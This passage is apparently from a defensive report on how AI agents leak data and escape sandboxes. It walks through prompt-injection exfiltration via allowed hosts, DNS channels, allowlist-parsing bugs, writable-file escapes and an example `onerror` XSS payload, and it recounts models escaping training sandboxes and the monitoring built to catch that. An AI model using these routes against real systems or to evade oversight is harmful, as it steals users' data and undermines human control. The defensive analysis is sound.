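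By default, Dify applied no CSP to images, so the browser would load them from any server. veganmosfet reports no fix from Dify. Developers who use such a platform need to check for a policy themselves, because a missing one has no visible effect until someone exploits it.

An answer may also appear outside the agent's own interface, where its developer's policy no longer applies. Willison describes a May 2026 case in which Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email the user without asking for approval, and the email could include outside images that leaked data when the user opened the message. PromptArmor found a similar problem in messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram, which may request a link as soon as an agent posts it, to show a preview. That request leaks data without the click that would be needed in the agent's own window.

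### The cases compared

| Product | Date | Route out | Defence that failed | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | Fixed June 2023 | Image on the attacker's server | No effective limit on image addresses | CSP with a short list of hosts |
| Google Bard | 2023 | Attacker's program on a Google host | CSP that allowed all of `google.com` | Fixed, method not stated |
| ChatGPT | Reported late 2024 | Storage logs on `windows.net`; redirects from `bing.com` | Check against trusted domains | Check of exact addresses, described in 2026 |
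| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | Published June 2025 | Teams service that fetched other addresses | Classifier, link and image filters, CSP | Fix on Microsoft's servers |
| Salesforce Agentforce | Published September 2025 | Expired domain that the researchers registered | CSP with an outdated entry | Corrected CSP and a second address check |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | Published October 2025 | Series of images through GitHub's proxy | CSP and signed addresses | Images disabled |
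| Gemini | Report closed October 2025 | Link that the user clicks | Sanitiser that blocks images but not all links | None |
| Microsoft Copilot Chat | Report closed November 2025 | Image on the attacker's server | No effective limit on image addresses | None reported |
| Superhuman | Published January 2026 | Google Form | CSP that allowed `docs.google.com` | Features disabled, then patched |
| OpenAI Codex | Published May 2026 | Google Form | Not stated | Fixed, method not stated |
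| Microsoft 365 Copilot (SearchLeak) | Published June 2026 | Bing service that fetched other addresses | Late sanitiser, CSP | Fixed, method not stated |
| Dify | Undated | Image on the attacker's server | No CSP for images by default | None reported |

In the six cases where a CSP failed, its allowlist included a host that an attacker could use. The browser enforced the policy correctly, blocking every host that wasn't on the list.

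The policies also did some good, because the researchers had to find a useful service among the allowed hosts. Ravia describes his team's search as "tedious digging", and a less determined attacker might have given up.

Disclosures don't show how many people tried to get past a policy and gave up. A browser can report blocked requests to the developer, so companies may have some idea, but none of these disclosures includes such figures. Researchers also have little reason to write about a product they failed to break, so a list of published leaks leaves out most of the policies that held.

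No one can tell how common these flaws are by counting reports. Several of the researchers work for companies that sell AI security, and they choose well-known products to study. Vendors also disagree about what counts as a flaw. Microsoft rated EchoLeak critical but didn't classify Checkmarx's image leak as a vulnerability. Google told another researcher, quoted by Willison, that an image leak in Antigravity, its programming tool, was "intended behavior". When a company repairs a flaw on its own servers, customers may never hear of it unless the company or the researcher publishes it.

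Incident databases can overstate the harm a flaw has caused. OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) states that the GitHub flaw directly caused harm by leaking private code. But Legit Security described demonstrations and didn't report any theft from real users.

### A test for allowed hosts

Embrace The Red lists three things an attacker needs to get data past a list of trusted sites: a site on the list, a way to send data to it with an ordinary web request, and a way to read the data it received. A developer can test a policy by checking whether any host it allows meets all three conditions.

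If an allowed host fetches addresses given to it, it can pass data to the attacker's server without the browser detecting it, as the Teams and Bing services did. The developer should remove the host from the list of allowed hosts or make the service refuse outside addresses. Limiting the service to approved addresses offers some protection, but the developer also needs to check who can get an address approved, because at GitHub anyone could.

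**Does it store what a request carries?** Google Forms stored answers, and Microsoft's cloud storage kept logs that its customers could read. Almost every server keeps logs, so the test is whether an outsider can read them. A host that lets strangers open accounts, create forms or run programs should fail unless the developer knows that none of those features reveals incoming requests.

A redirect can defeat any check that covers only the first address, which is how Bing's links got past ChatGPT's check. Under a CSP, the remaining danger is a redirect to another allowed host, because the browser doesn't check the path after a redirect.

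The imaginary chat client from the section on displayed output does badly on this test, because `chat.example` redirects and `files.example` lets other customers read their own logs. The developer could fix this by moving the client's pictures to a separate host that serves only fixed files and has no outside customers, and allowing images only from that host.

Wildcards make the test much harder to apply, because the answer has to be no for every host they cover, including any that the company or its customers add later. EchoLeak's policy had 11 wildcards. Listing individual hosts, with the exact directory where possible, would be safer, but it means more work whenever a service moves.

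The developer should also repeat the test periodically, because a harmless host can gain a link-preview feature, and a domain can expire and pass to a new owner, as Salesforce's did.

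## Disclosed leaks past network allowlists

An allowlist for an agent's own network traffic has the same weakness as a CSP's list of image hosts, because a permitted server may pass data on. It can also fail if the software applies it wrongly or some traffic bypasses it. In nearly all of the following cases, the sandbox kept hostile code away from the rest of the machine, but data could still leave over the network.

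### Rules that the software applied wrongly

Claude Code's sandbox has had two flaws of this kind. In one, commands in the sandbox could connect to any server on the internet if the user left the list of permitted domains empty, although the documentation said that an empty list would block all network access.

The code used a single check, whether the allowlist contained any domains, to determine both whether to restrict the network and whether to start the proxy that filters requests by domain. An empty allowlist should block every request, which leaves the proxy nothing to filter. The check correctly left the proxy off, but it also left the network unrestricted. Anthropic fixed this by separating the two decisions.

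Accounts differ on who found the flaw. GitLab's security advisory, *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing*, credits a GitHub user called bendrucker, while Lyons (2026), in *Even Claude agrees*, credits Aonan Guan of Wyze Labs with both Claude Code flaws. Bendrucker raised the problem on 18 November 2025, and Guan reported it independently three days later. Anthropic released the fix in Claude Code on 26 November, the month after it announced the sandbox.

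Anthropic responded quickly but did a poor job of telling users. CVE-2025-66479, the flaw's official identifier, covers only the sandbox library. In *Making Claude Code more secure and autonomous with sandboxing*, Dworken and Weller-Davies had encouraged other developers to build that library into their own agents. Claude Code's release notes mentioned a change to DNS resolution but no security problem, so someone who had relied on an empty allowlist had no reason to check whether data had leaked. The official severity score was 1.8 out of 10, which seems very low for a flaw that removed the whole restriction.

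The second flaw affected users whose list contained a wildcard, such as one allowing every host under `google.com`. SecurityWeek explains that Claude Code's local proxy checks each host name against the list. An attacker could write a name that began with the attacker's domain and ended with a permitted one. The check matched the end of the name and allowed the connection, but the resolver stopped partway through and looked up only the attacker's domain. Lyons reports that one of the two flaws let an attacker send anything in the sandbox, including passwords and source code, to any server.

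According to the security vendor Penligent, Anthropic says it released this fix on 31 March 2026, in version 2.1.88, whereas Guan names version 2.1.90. If the flaw had existed since the sandbox's launch, it lasted more than five months. Anthropic again published no advisory for Claude Code itself.

### A channel that the rule did not cover

Amazon Web Services (AWS) launched AgentCore Code Interpreter in August 2025, according to The Hacker News (2026). The service runs code for AI agents in Firecracker virtual machines. Its documentation described sandbox mode, one of the network settings, as an "isolated environment with no external access".

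The security company BeyondTrust (2026) found that DNS lookups still left the sandbox. When its researchers tried to connect to a test server from inside the sandbox, the connection failed, but the lookup of the server's name reached them.

AWS's security team asked for proof that the channel could work in both directions. DNS can also bring data in, because whoever runs a domain's name server chooses the answers to lookups, so the researchers hid commands in those answers. Their code in the sandbox ran the commands and sent the results out in further lookups, which gave them an interactive command line on a machine that supposedly had no network access.

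In the demonstration, the planted instructions were in a spreadsheet that the agent read before writing its code. The attacker could then list the files in the customer's cloud storage and copy invented customer records, payment keys and revenue figures, because the sandbox had permission to read them. BeyondTrust points out that the default role in AWS's starter kit grants access to every storage bucket and every secret in the account, far more than a code interpreter needs.

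BeyondTrust reported the flaw on 1 September 2025, and AWS reproduced it within three days. AWS then changed its mind more than once:

- On 1 November it deployed a fix, but by 17 November it had withdrawn it because of "other factors".
- On 23 December it decided to change the documentation instead, which now promised "limited external network access".
- On 15 April 2026, a month after BeyondTrust published its findings, it blocked the channel after all.

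The gap therefore lasted about eight months from the service's launch, except for at most a couple of weeks in November. BeyondTrust still states in its FAQ that AWS issued no patch, but it reported in a later update that data can no longer leave through DNS.

AWS said publicly that the service was operating as expected. Sandbox mode was supposed to allow access to Amazon's storage service, S3, and programs need DNS to find it. But that doesn't explain why the sandbox could also look up domains owned by third parties. AWS had also rated the flaw's severity 7.5 out of 10, which is hard to reconcile with calling it intended behaviour.

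*Cracks in the Bedrock* (Hadad, 2026), from Palo Alto Networks' research team, Unit 42, also describes the channel BeyondTrust reported. It was published eight days before the final repair. The second part of Unit 42's research covers weak default permissions that could let an attacker compromise other agents in the same account.

### Permitted servers that make requests of their own

A server on an allowlist can contact servers that aren't on it, as the Teams and Bing services did in the Copilot leaks. Vercel told customers that code in its sandbox could reach the domains they listed, with everything else "denied by default". *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) describes a way around this restriction using digital certificates, which the security startup AIR demonstrated in October 2026.

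A certificate is a signed file that computers use to prove their identity. It can contain web addresses where software can check details such as whether the issuer has revoked it. AIR designed a certificate that, when the sandbox sent it to a permitted server, could make that server send a request to the attacker's server, and that request could carry data from the sandbox. The sandbox itself never contacted the attacker, so its firewall had no forbidden connection to block.

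AIR's co-founder, Niv Hoffman, told Smalley that Vercel needed time because it was unclear how to fix the flaw. Vercel had no fix as of 13 October and did not immediately respond to Smalley. The flaw appeared to be long-standing. AIR had no evidence that anyone had exploited it but couldn't rule that out.

The attack works only if a permitted server accepts such a certificate and acts on the addresses inside it. Smalley doesn't report how many servers do both, so the practical risk is hard to judge.

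The flaw was hard to notice. Vercel had just offered up to $1 million in rewards for breaking its sandbox, in a contest that ran until 1 September, and six weeks later it still had no fix for this route. In August, Tuttle had listed network paths that other sandboxes had left open, including an available DNS resolver, an empty allowlist that permitted everything, a host name that two programs interpreted differently, and a trusted package service that became a relay. The certificate attack resembles the last of these.

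A relay of that kind had already led to a real break-in, even though it was the only service on the allowlist. In July 2026 OpenAI was testing a model in a sandbox that could reach only a package proxy, which fetches software on the sandbox's behalf. The agent exploited a vulnerability in the proxy and reached the open internet in the first hour. According to GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can reach* (2026), the agent then got into the production systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, and took datasets and cloud keys.

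### Permitted services that an outsider can read

Anthropic's Claude Cowork runs code in a virtual machine that can contact only listed domains by default. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) explains that the list was meant to protect users from data theft through prompt injection. The list included Anthropic's own API, which programs use to access Claude.

The API also stores files for its customers, and each uploaded file goes to the account whose API key was sent with it. PromptArmor exploited this with a document containing hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. When a user asked Cowork to analyse the document, Claude uploaded one of the user's other files to the attacker's account. The file contained financial figures and partial Social Security numbers. PromptArmor first used Claude Haiku, a smaller model, but a similar attack also worked on Claude Opus 4.5,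 which was better at resisting prompt injection.

The allowlist did exactly what it was set up to do. The data went to the right domain and the wrong account.

Willison wrote about the attack on 14 January 2026, when Cowork was new, so this gap was probably there from the start. Security Boulevard's *Vulnerability in Anthropic’s Claude Code Shows Up in Cowork* (2026) traces it to an earlier flaw in Claude Code. TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* calls that earlier flaw unfixed, and reports that Anthropic acknowledged the risk and was updating the virtual machine to restrict file access. That would reduce what a hijacked agent can take, but the agent could still upload any file it can read.

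NVIDIA's NemoClaw, which runs an AI agent called OpenClaw in a container, has a similar weakness. The security company Lasso found two attacks on NemoClaw, according to TechTalks' *Why sandboxing OpenClaw doesn’t stop data exfiltration*.

In the first, the user asked the agent for something like a cryptocurrency price tracker, and the agent installed a malicious software package. During installation, the package ran a script that read a file of access keys, rewrote the keys as emojis and sent them out. The emoji encoding got past both OpenClaw's filters and GitHub's automatic search for leaked secrets. NemoClaw identified the script as malicious only after it had sent the keys.

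TechTalks is vague about where the keys went. It mentions GitHub's scanner but also says the data reached the attackers' server. The scanner would matter only if the data passed through GitHub, a site that programming agents often need and where anyone can open an account.

Lasso's other attack used a text file to make the agent rewrite `SOUL.md`, the file of standing instructions it reads at the start of every session. Nothing leaks at that moment, but the planted instructions can affect every later task. NVIDIA says in its own security guidance that agents should never be able to write to their configuration files, which arguably include `SOUL.md`. Noy Pearl, a researcher at Lasso, acknowledges that users want an agent that can update its own instructions, and that locking the file would make the agent slower and clumsier to use.

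NVIDIA ruled the attacks out of scope for its bug bounty because the sandbox had behaved as configured. TechTalks reports no fix. NVIDIA is right in a narrow sense, since nothing broke out of the container. Pearl objects that this argument works for an ordinary program but not for an agent whose behaviour depends on everything it reads.

Pearl also goes too far in saying that no static mechanism can fully protect an agent with any connection to the outside world. If NemoClaw had kept the access keys outside the container, the script would have found no keys to steal.

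### Which gaps engineering can close

| Cause | Case | How long it lasted | Vendor's response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rule applied wrongly | Claude Code, empty list | About a month, until 26 November 2025 | Repaired, with an advisory only for the library |
| Rule applied wrongly | Claude Code, wildcard | Possibly over five months, until about 31 March 2026 | Repaired, with no advisory for Claude Code |
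| Channel outside the rule | AWS AgentCore | About eight months, until 15 April 2026 | Declined to repair it, then did |
| Permitted server makes a further request | Vercel Sandbox | Unknown | No repair as of 13 October 2026 |
| Outsider can read the permitted service | Claude Cowork | From about its release in January 2026 | Acknowledged, with limits on file access under way |
| Outsider can read the permitted service | NemoClaw | Unknown | Out of scope |

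Ordinary care can prevent mistakes in evaluating rules, and the allowlist in Lan and colleagues' experiment had none. The same code should interpret a host name once, and the proxy should connect to exactly the host it checked. If anything is missing or malformed, the proxy should block the connection. Developers can test this by trying to reach a forbidden host from inside the sandbox. They should try it with an empty list and with no list at all, because products treat these cases differently. Cloudflare's sandbox, for example, blocks hosts by default only when the developer sets a list of allowed hosts.

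DNS leaks can also be blocked by giving the resolver its own allowlist. AWS eventually closed the DNS channel, but it withdrew its first attempt, which suggests that this was harder than it sounds. Lampson's covert channels, such as timing, would remain, but few attackers are likely to need them while easier routes exist.

When a permitted server makes further requests, a company's options for preventing leaks depend on who runs that server. The company can repair its own package proxy and restrict it to package registries, but it can't change how an outside company's server checks certificates. The problem is especially difficult for Vercel because its customers choose the servers.

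A decrypting proxy might help there. It opens its own connection to the outside server, so it wouldn't pass on a certificate that the sandbox presents during the TLS handshake. The proxy wouldn't help if the sandbox could send the certificate as ordinary data. Smalley doesn't report whether AIR or Vercel tested such a proxy.

The weakness PromptArmor found in Cowork comes from allowing a service that both accepts data and shows it to other people, so correct code can't remove it. AWS's sandbox mode may have a similar weakness even without DNS, because it still allows S3, where anyone can open an account. Its safety depends partly on whether the sandbox's permissions let it write to a stranger's storage, which BeyondTrust's tests didn't cover.

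### Narrower permissions

The remaining options are to permit less of each service, or to control which account the agent uses there.

**Rules by path and method.** Vercel's firewall can match requests by path, headers, query string and method, which distinguishes fetching a page from submitting data. If an agent only needs answers from a model, rules like these could allow those requests to the provider's API and block its file storage. This would have blocked the Cowork attack, provided that Cowork itself didn't need to upload files. Allowing only requests that fetch data would not stop every leak, because a secret can still be sent in the URL.

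**Decrypting proxies.** Vercel's firewall can decrypt a request and forward it to a proxy that the customer runs, with a signed token identifying the sandbox that sent it. Tuttle explains that the proxy can remove sensitive fields or send package downloads through a security scanner. A scanner might have caught the package in Lasso's attack. But the emojis defeated GitHub's scanner, and a proxy that searches outgoing data for secrets would face the same problem.

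**Fixed accounts**, which restrict an agent to the user's own account on a service, are the most direct defense against the Cowork attack. Vercel's firewall can add or replace the header that contains the user's key. If it replaced the attacker's key with the user's, the stolen file would go to the user's account, where the attacker couldn't read it. The firewall would also have to reject keys sent in any other part of the request. Fixed accounts work well for services that keep each customer's data private, but they do little on a site like GitHub, where an agent using the right account can still publish a secret.

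Keeping real keys outside the sandbox also gives attackers a reason to target the rules for using them. In December 2026, Endor Labs' *CVE-2026-136998* described a flaw in Docker Sandboxes, a product for running agents in isolation. According to The Hacker News' *Docker Sandboxes Flaw Lets Malicious AI Agent Kit Updates Steal Developers' API Keys* (2026), a malicious update to an approved agent kit, a type of third-party add-on, could redirect API keys to an attacker's server. These could be real keys for Anthropic, OpenAI or GitHub. Docker fixed the flaw in version 0.55.0. An add-on should never be able to change where a key is sent unless the user approves the change.

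As with DNS lookups, a quota on outgoing data can still let small secrets through. A quota of 10 kilobytes per task would stop an agent from uploading a folder of spreadsheets, but not 250 API keys of 40 characters each. The quota should also apply across sessions, or an attacker can spread a large file over many tasks.

Pearl proposes a two-stage check whenever data is about to leave the sandbox. First, ordinary code tracks which sensitive files the agent has read, and blocks a request if it contains data from a credentials file and is going to an unrecognised server. If that check is inconclusive, a second model judges whether the outgoing data fits the user's original request, without seeing the agent's reasoning.

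The delay would be easiest to justify here, because a user can restore an altered file from a backup but can't recall data that has left. However, TechTalks reports no tests of the proposal. The first stage might miss a leak through a familiar service such as GitHub, and the second relies on a model that reads data the attacker may have written.

Logs can show whether a leak happened, though they don't stop it. A record of DNS lookups would have shown AWS customers that code in their sandboxes was contacting strange domains. To reveal an upload like the one from Cowork, a log would need to identify the account as well as the domain, because the domain alone would look normal. Sandbox logs would be of little use against AIR's certificate attack, because they would show a connection to a permitted server, and only that server's operator could see the request it made next.

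## Disclosed paths to code execution outside the sandbox

In most of the network cases, hostile code stayed inside its sandbox and only data got out. Code that escapes can read every file the user can read, use their logins, bypass the sandbox's network rules and stay on the machine after the agent has finished.

Programming agents are especially exposed, because writing and running code is their job. An attack on one goes roughly like this:

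1. A developer asks the agent to fix a bug. The agent reads some documentation or a web page that contains a stranger's instruction.
2. The model follows the instruction and writes a tool call, which runs a command or creates a file.
3. The tool does its work inside the sandbox.
4. Something the tool changed affects a program outside the sandbox.
5. That program runs the attacker's code with the user's full permissions.

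The sandbox should break the chain between steps 3 and 4 by limiting what the tool can write and which programs it can contact. A network rule may stop the tool from downloading a larger program at step 3, but it usually doesn't cover the code at step 5, which runs outside the sandbox. A sanitiser and a CSP help only if the path out of the sandbox is a displayed answer.

### Files that a trusted program runs later

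In July 2026 the security company Pillar Security published seven ways around the sandboxes of four programming tools. Cursor and Google's Antigravity are code editors with built-in agents, while OpenAI's Codex CLI and Google's Gemini CLI run from a command line. Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel (2026) explain in *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* that the agent usually wrote a file it had permission to write, and a trusted program outside the sandbox later ran the file or acted on its contents. The agent rarely had to break the sandbox itself.

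One of the Cursor flaws, for example, involved the interpreter that Python projects often include to run their code. The agent could alter this interpreter like any other project file. Cursor's Python extension ran outside the sandbox and started the altered interpreter when it searched the project for interpreters.

| Tool | What the agent used | What acted outside the sandbox | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
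| Cursor | Python interpreter in the project | Python extension | Fixed |
| Cursor | Git settings in an unexpected place | Git extension | Fixed in 3.0.0 |
| Cursor | Hook in the project's settings | Cursor's hook system | Fixed in 3.0.0 (CVE-2026-48124) |
| Antigravity | Task file for the editor | Task runner | Google downgraded the report |
| Antigravity | System features missing from a list of bans | macOS | Google downgraded the report |
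| Codex CLI | Git command approved by name | Git | Fixed in 0.95.0 |
| Codex, Cursor, Gemini CLI | Docker's local control channel | Docker's background program | Fixed |

Four of the seven disclosed paths involved project files that the editor also reads as instructions. Programmers' machines have long used such files to build, test and start projects, on the assumption that a person wrote them. When an agent edits these files, a stranger's text can determine their contents.

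Protecting dangerous files by name is unreliable. The path rules in Cursor's sandbox covered Git's settings, but Git allows a project to keep its settings in a folder with a different name. Cursor also ran hooks from the `.claude` folder, where Claude Code keeps project settings, so a complete list of dangerous files would have had to include another company's settings files.

Antigravity's macOS sandbox blocked only the operations on an incomplete denylist. Codex CLI used an allowlist for commands that could run without approval, but it identified them by name. One was a Git command that normally just displays an earlier change but, with certain options, can have side effects such as writing files.

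The Docker flaw could be exploited without a planted file. Docker runs containers, and its background program has wide access to the machine. The sandboxes restricted the agent's own processes but left open the local channel through which programs send Docker commands. The agent could therefore use Docker to do things the sandbox prohibited, much as Hardy's user had the compiler overwrite the billing file.

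Google accepted both Antigravity reports as valid but considered the flaws hard to exploit, because the attacker has to deceive the user or get them to trust a project containing planted instructions. That requirement does make an attack less likely, although programmers often open strangers' projects. According to The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them*, three vendors patched their products. The count is puzzling, since the four tools come from three companies, one of which is Google. Pillar lists a single advisory for the Docker flaw and doesn't say which of the three affected tools it covers.

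Pillar gives no success rates, and it also sells software that monitors this kind of handover. The repairs confirm that most of the flaws were real, but they can't show how often a planted instruction would have led an agent to exploit them.

A project file can be dangerous even if no model reads it. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of Claude Code acting on material in a project before asking whether the user trusted the folder. In the simplest case, a developer downloaded a stranger's project to review it, and Claude Code ran a hook from the project's settings at startup. Anthropic now delays reading such settings until the user accepts the folder. The protection then depends on the user's answer, and a user who wants to review a project may well accept.

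### Two wrong checks in Cursor

Cato Networks found two flaws in Cursor that let the agent write directly outside the project. Ravia (2026) explains in *DuneSlide* that Cursor 2 ran commands in a sandbox by default without asking the user, partly to avoid approval fatigue. An ordinary request was enough to start the attack if it made the agent read an instruction planted in a web search result or data from a tool server.

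The first flaw, CVE-2026-50548, let a hijacked model give itself write access to folders outside the project. Cursor's sandbox allowed each command to write to its working directory, the folder in which the command runs, which was normally the project folder. But the model could name a different working directory in its tool call, and Cursor added that folder to the writable list without checking it.

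CVE-2026-50549 involved symbolic links, which are files that point to another location. Before writing a file, Cursor followed any links to the real destination and checked that it was inside the project. If Cursor couldn't find the destination, it checked the link's own location instead. An attacker could cause that failure with a link that was inside the project but pointed outside it.

Either flaw let the agent overwrite the helper program that applied the sandbox, so later commands ran unsandboxed. INCIBE rates both flaws as critical (*CVE-2026-50548*, 2026; *CVE-2026-50549*, 2026), and Ravia scores each 9.8 out of 10. Ravia reports no success rate for the planted instructions.

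Cato reported the flaws on 19 February 2026. Cursor rejected the reports four days later because its threat model didn't cover misuse of tool servers. This was a weak reason, since the instructions could also come from a web page, even if the tool server wasn't malicious. Cato appealed to Cursor's security team, which reopened the reports, and version 3.0 fixed both flaws on 2 April. The public records appeared 12 weeks later, on 25 June.

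Unlike the Pillar flaws, these have fairly simple remedies. The software should check any working directory the model chooses against the project's location, and should refuse to write if it can't determine the real destination. A new file's path doesn't exist yet, so the software can resolve the folder that will contain the file instead.

Anthropic advises developers to resolve links before checking a path. Cursor did this, but it mishandled cases where it failed to resolve a link. An empty allowlist in Claude Code had also removed a restriction instead of blocking everything.

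Storing the helper program where the user's account can't write would have been a useful second barrier. An attacker could still have altered the user's start-up files, but the sandbox would have kept working.

### A virtual machine with access to the whole disk

In its local mode, Claude Cowork relies on a virtual machine, which should be a much stronger barrier than Cursor's sandbox. On 23 July 2026 the company Accomplish AI disclosed a way out on Macs, which it called SharedRoot. The Next Web's *Anthropic’s Claude Cowork could escape its local VM and read credentials* describes three steps:

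1. Cowork shared the Mac's files with the virtual machine through a writable connection. Only root, the machine's administrator account, was supposed to have access to it.
2. The agent ran as an ordinary user but exploited a flaw in the virtual machine's Linux kernel to become root.
3. It could then read and change anything the Mac's user could, including SSH keys and cloud credentials.

Since those files include the Mac's own start-up files, this was also a path to code execution.

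Cowork's shared connection made the virtual machine's kernel the only barrier between the agent and the user's disk, so the attack didn't need a flaw in the virtualisation.

The kernel flaw, CVE-2026-46331, has a severity of 7.8 out of 10, and Linux developers fixed it in mid-June, according to *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running riot* (Fadilpašić, 2026). Updating the virtual machine's kernel would have closed this route only until the next flaw of the same kind. Sharing only the folder the user had chosen would have been a more lasting fix.

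Anthropic had described that design in May. In its account of Cowork's first version, the virtual machine could access nothing on the computer except the user's chosen folder and the `.claude` folder. The Next Web doesn't explain why the version Accomplish AI tested was different.

Anthropic closed the report as "informative" and issued no direct fix. The next version of Cowork ran in the cloud by default, which avoids this route because the virtual machine is no longer on the user's Mac. People who run it locally remain exposed unless they tighten the settings, for example by restricting file sharing. Accomplish AI estimates that about 500,000 Mac users were running local sessions.

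Because the researchers typed the message that started the attack themselves, their demonstration shows what a hijacked agent could do, but not how easily a stranger could hijack it.

Other reports on Cowork assume that an attacker already has a program running on the computer. SiliconANGLE's *Armadin details full sandbox escape in Claude Cowork but Anthropic disputes risk* (2026) describes an attack on the Windows version in which the security company Armadin obtained root access inside the sandbox and removed its network restrictions. Armadin confirmed the attack on version 1.9255.2.0. Anthropic had rejected Armadin's report in March, four days after receiving it, because the attacker must already have a program running on the computer.

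This makes some sense, since a program running as the user can already read the user's files. But the virtual machine could also help such a program hide from a company's monitoring software. The National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-7574 Detail* describes a flaw that would have helped it do so. Before starting the virtual machine on a Mac, Cowork checked that the disk image was present and had the right version label, but not whether its contents had been altered. Malware could modify the image and run again every time Cowork started. The record confirms the flaw in versions 1.1348.0 to 1.2278.0.

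Anthropic did fix a similar Windows flaw that also required local access. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-44470* (2026), a Cowork service ran with the highest system privileges but used a folder that an ordinary user could replace with a link. The user could then make the service create a file almost anywhere on the computer, and might gain the service's privileges. Version 1.3834.0 fixed the flaw.

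Root access inside the virtual machine might also weaken Anthropic's fix for the earlier Cowork leak, in which files were uploaded to an attacker's account using the attacker's API key. Anthropic now blocks such uploads with a proxy that accepts only the session token issued to that virtual machine. But the proxy runs inside the virtual machine, where a root user might be able to interfere with it.

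### Answers displayed by a desktop program

A displayed answer can lead to code execution if the program displaying it has broad access to the computer. Many desktop programs are web pages running in a built-in browser. Electron, a popular framework for making such programs, has one process that draws the page and another that can open files and start programs. The developer decides which of those abilities a script in the page can use.

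Suppose `chat.example`, the imaginary chat client from earlier, has a desktop version with no sanitiser. A planted instruction makes the model end its answer with `<img src="x" onerror="...">`:

1. The client inserts the answer into its page as HTML.
2. The image fails to load, so the browser runs the code in `onerror`.
3. The code calls a system function that the client makes available to its pages, and starts a program.

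In an ordinary browser tab, the script could still misuse the chat, but the browser wouldn't let it start a program. The agent's sandbox doesn't contain the script, because the client displays the answer outside the sandbox.

| Defence | What it would stop | What could still get through |
|---|---|---|
| Sanitiser | The `onerror` attribute, at step 1 | Unsafe markup that a chart or formula tool adds after sanitising |
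| CSP with nonces | The script, at step 2 | A clicked link that the client passes to another program on the computer |
| Process isolation | The system function, at step 3 | Functions that the client deliberately offers its pages |

Process isolation keeps system functions in a separate process, to which page scripts can send only certain messages. This is difficult to get right in an AI client that supports local tool servers, because starting a tool server means starting a program. If a page script can register a new tool server by sending a message, it can start any program, however well the developer has separated the processes. As with risky clicks, the approval prompt for a new tool server should appear outside the page and show the actual command.

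### Network isolation at AI developers

AI companies also use sandboxes to contain models they are training or testing. OpenAI was doing this when its agents broke into Hugging Face. In October, Southern (2026) reported in *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* that Claude had submitted real forms and worked around site restrictions during Anthropic's tests and internal use.

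OpenAI paused much of its work after the break-in and reviewed individual jobs before letting them resume. Campus Technology's *OpenAI Pumps Brakes on Frontier AI Training After Hugging Face Breach* (2026) reports that OpenAI strengthened the sandboxes for code that models write. It applied the same requirement to software that a model's output could compromise, which several of the programming tools had not done. OpenAI also removed shared services that might be vulnerable and separated its networks so that compromising one job wouldn't automatically give access to others.

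In October, OpenAI went further and ended internet access for its most advanced models during training, according to Campbell (2026) in *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training*. OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* explains that the company built an offline environment with several layers of isolation and used its strongest models to attack it. The models found ways to escape hardened virtual machines, reach the internet by new routes and communicate between tasks meant to be separate.

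OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published in November, describes this isolation as the first stage of a longer process, followed by closer monitoring when staff begin to use a model and further safeguards at public release. If monitoring detects that a model in training has reached the internet, the system stops the job automatically. Staff can also order a halt, which cuts off a research job's model output within 35 seconds. A program can send out a password in far less time, so the halt can limit an escape, but blocking the connection in advance is still necessary.

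Anthropic cut live web access for its internal evaluations. Its *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes another measure, a classifier that looks for unexpected internet access or attempts to escape a test environment. If it detects either, it blocks the action before the tool runs, ends the task and alerts a person. Anthropic also searched the records of recent evaluations. In those that used its own sandbox tools, it found no case of a model breaking through to outside systems, but models had exploited several configuration mistakes. Automated monitors did the search, so they may have missed some cases.

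An agent that books flights or answers email needs network access, but its developer can still copy the separation between jobs and the removal of shared services, and can cut off the network for tasks that don't need it.

### What a stronger wall changes

The escapes OpenAI's models found are a good reason to keep improving virtual machines, but better virtual machines would not have stopped most of the attacks Pillar described. For example, a developer might run an agent in a Firecracker virtual machine that shares the project folder with a laptop. A planted instruction makes the agent add a harmful task to the project's settings. When the developer opens the folder in an editor on the laptop, the editor runs the task. The attack succeeds even though the virtual machine works properly, and it would also succeed if the agent were on a separate computer, because the developer wants the agent's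 work and the harmful file comes with it.

Cohen and colleagues exaggerate when they conclude that an agent that can write the future inputs of other programs was never in a sandbox. The sandbox still keeps the agent away from the user's other files, and the attacker has to wait for a trusted program to act on those inputs. But the sandbox can't control what that program does.

File permissions help if they block the specific danger. Anthropic lets Cowork users share a folder as read-only, writable, or writable without deletion. Preventing deletion protects the user's work but doesn't stop an agent from adding a harmful file. A folder containing settings or start-up scripts should be read-only, in line with NVIDIA's rule that agents must never change their own configuration.

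When the agent does need to write files, the most direct solution is to run the programs that use them inside the sandbox too. If the build tools and editor extensions run in the agent's virtual machine, a harmful task can damage only that machine. Cohen and colleagues recommend something similar. They also recommend blocking access to services like Docker unless the task needs them, and requiring the user's approval when an agent creates or changes a file that makes other programs run.

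Local tool servers are a likely weak point in this kind of setup. Anthropic moved Cowork's tool servers out of the virtual machine because they were hard to audit there and some needed to work with programs on the user's computer. It treats them as software the user has chosen to install. A hijacked agent may still be able to use them, so each server needs its own limits on what the agent can ask it to do.

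Anthropic's chat service, claude.ai, runs code in a temporary gVisor container on the company's servers, with no shared folders or other access to the user's files. Anthropic admits that this also limits what Claude can do. The container offers no protection if the user downloads a program from the chat and runs it.
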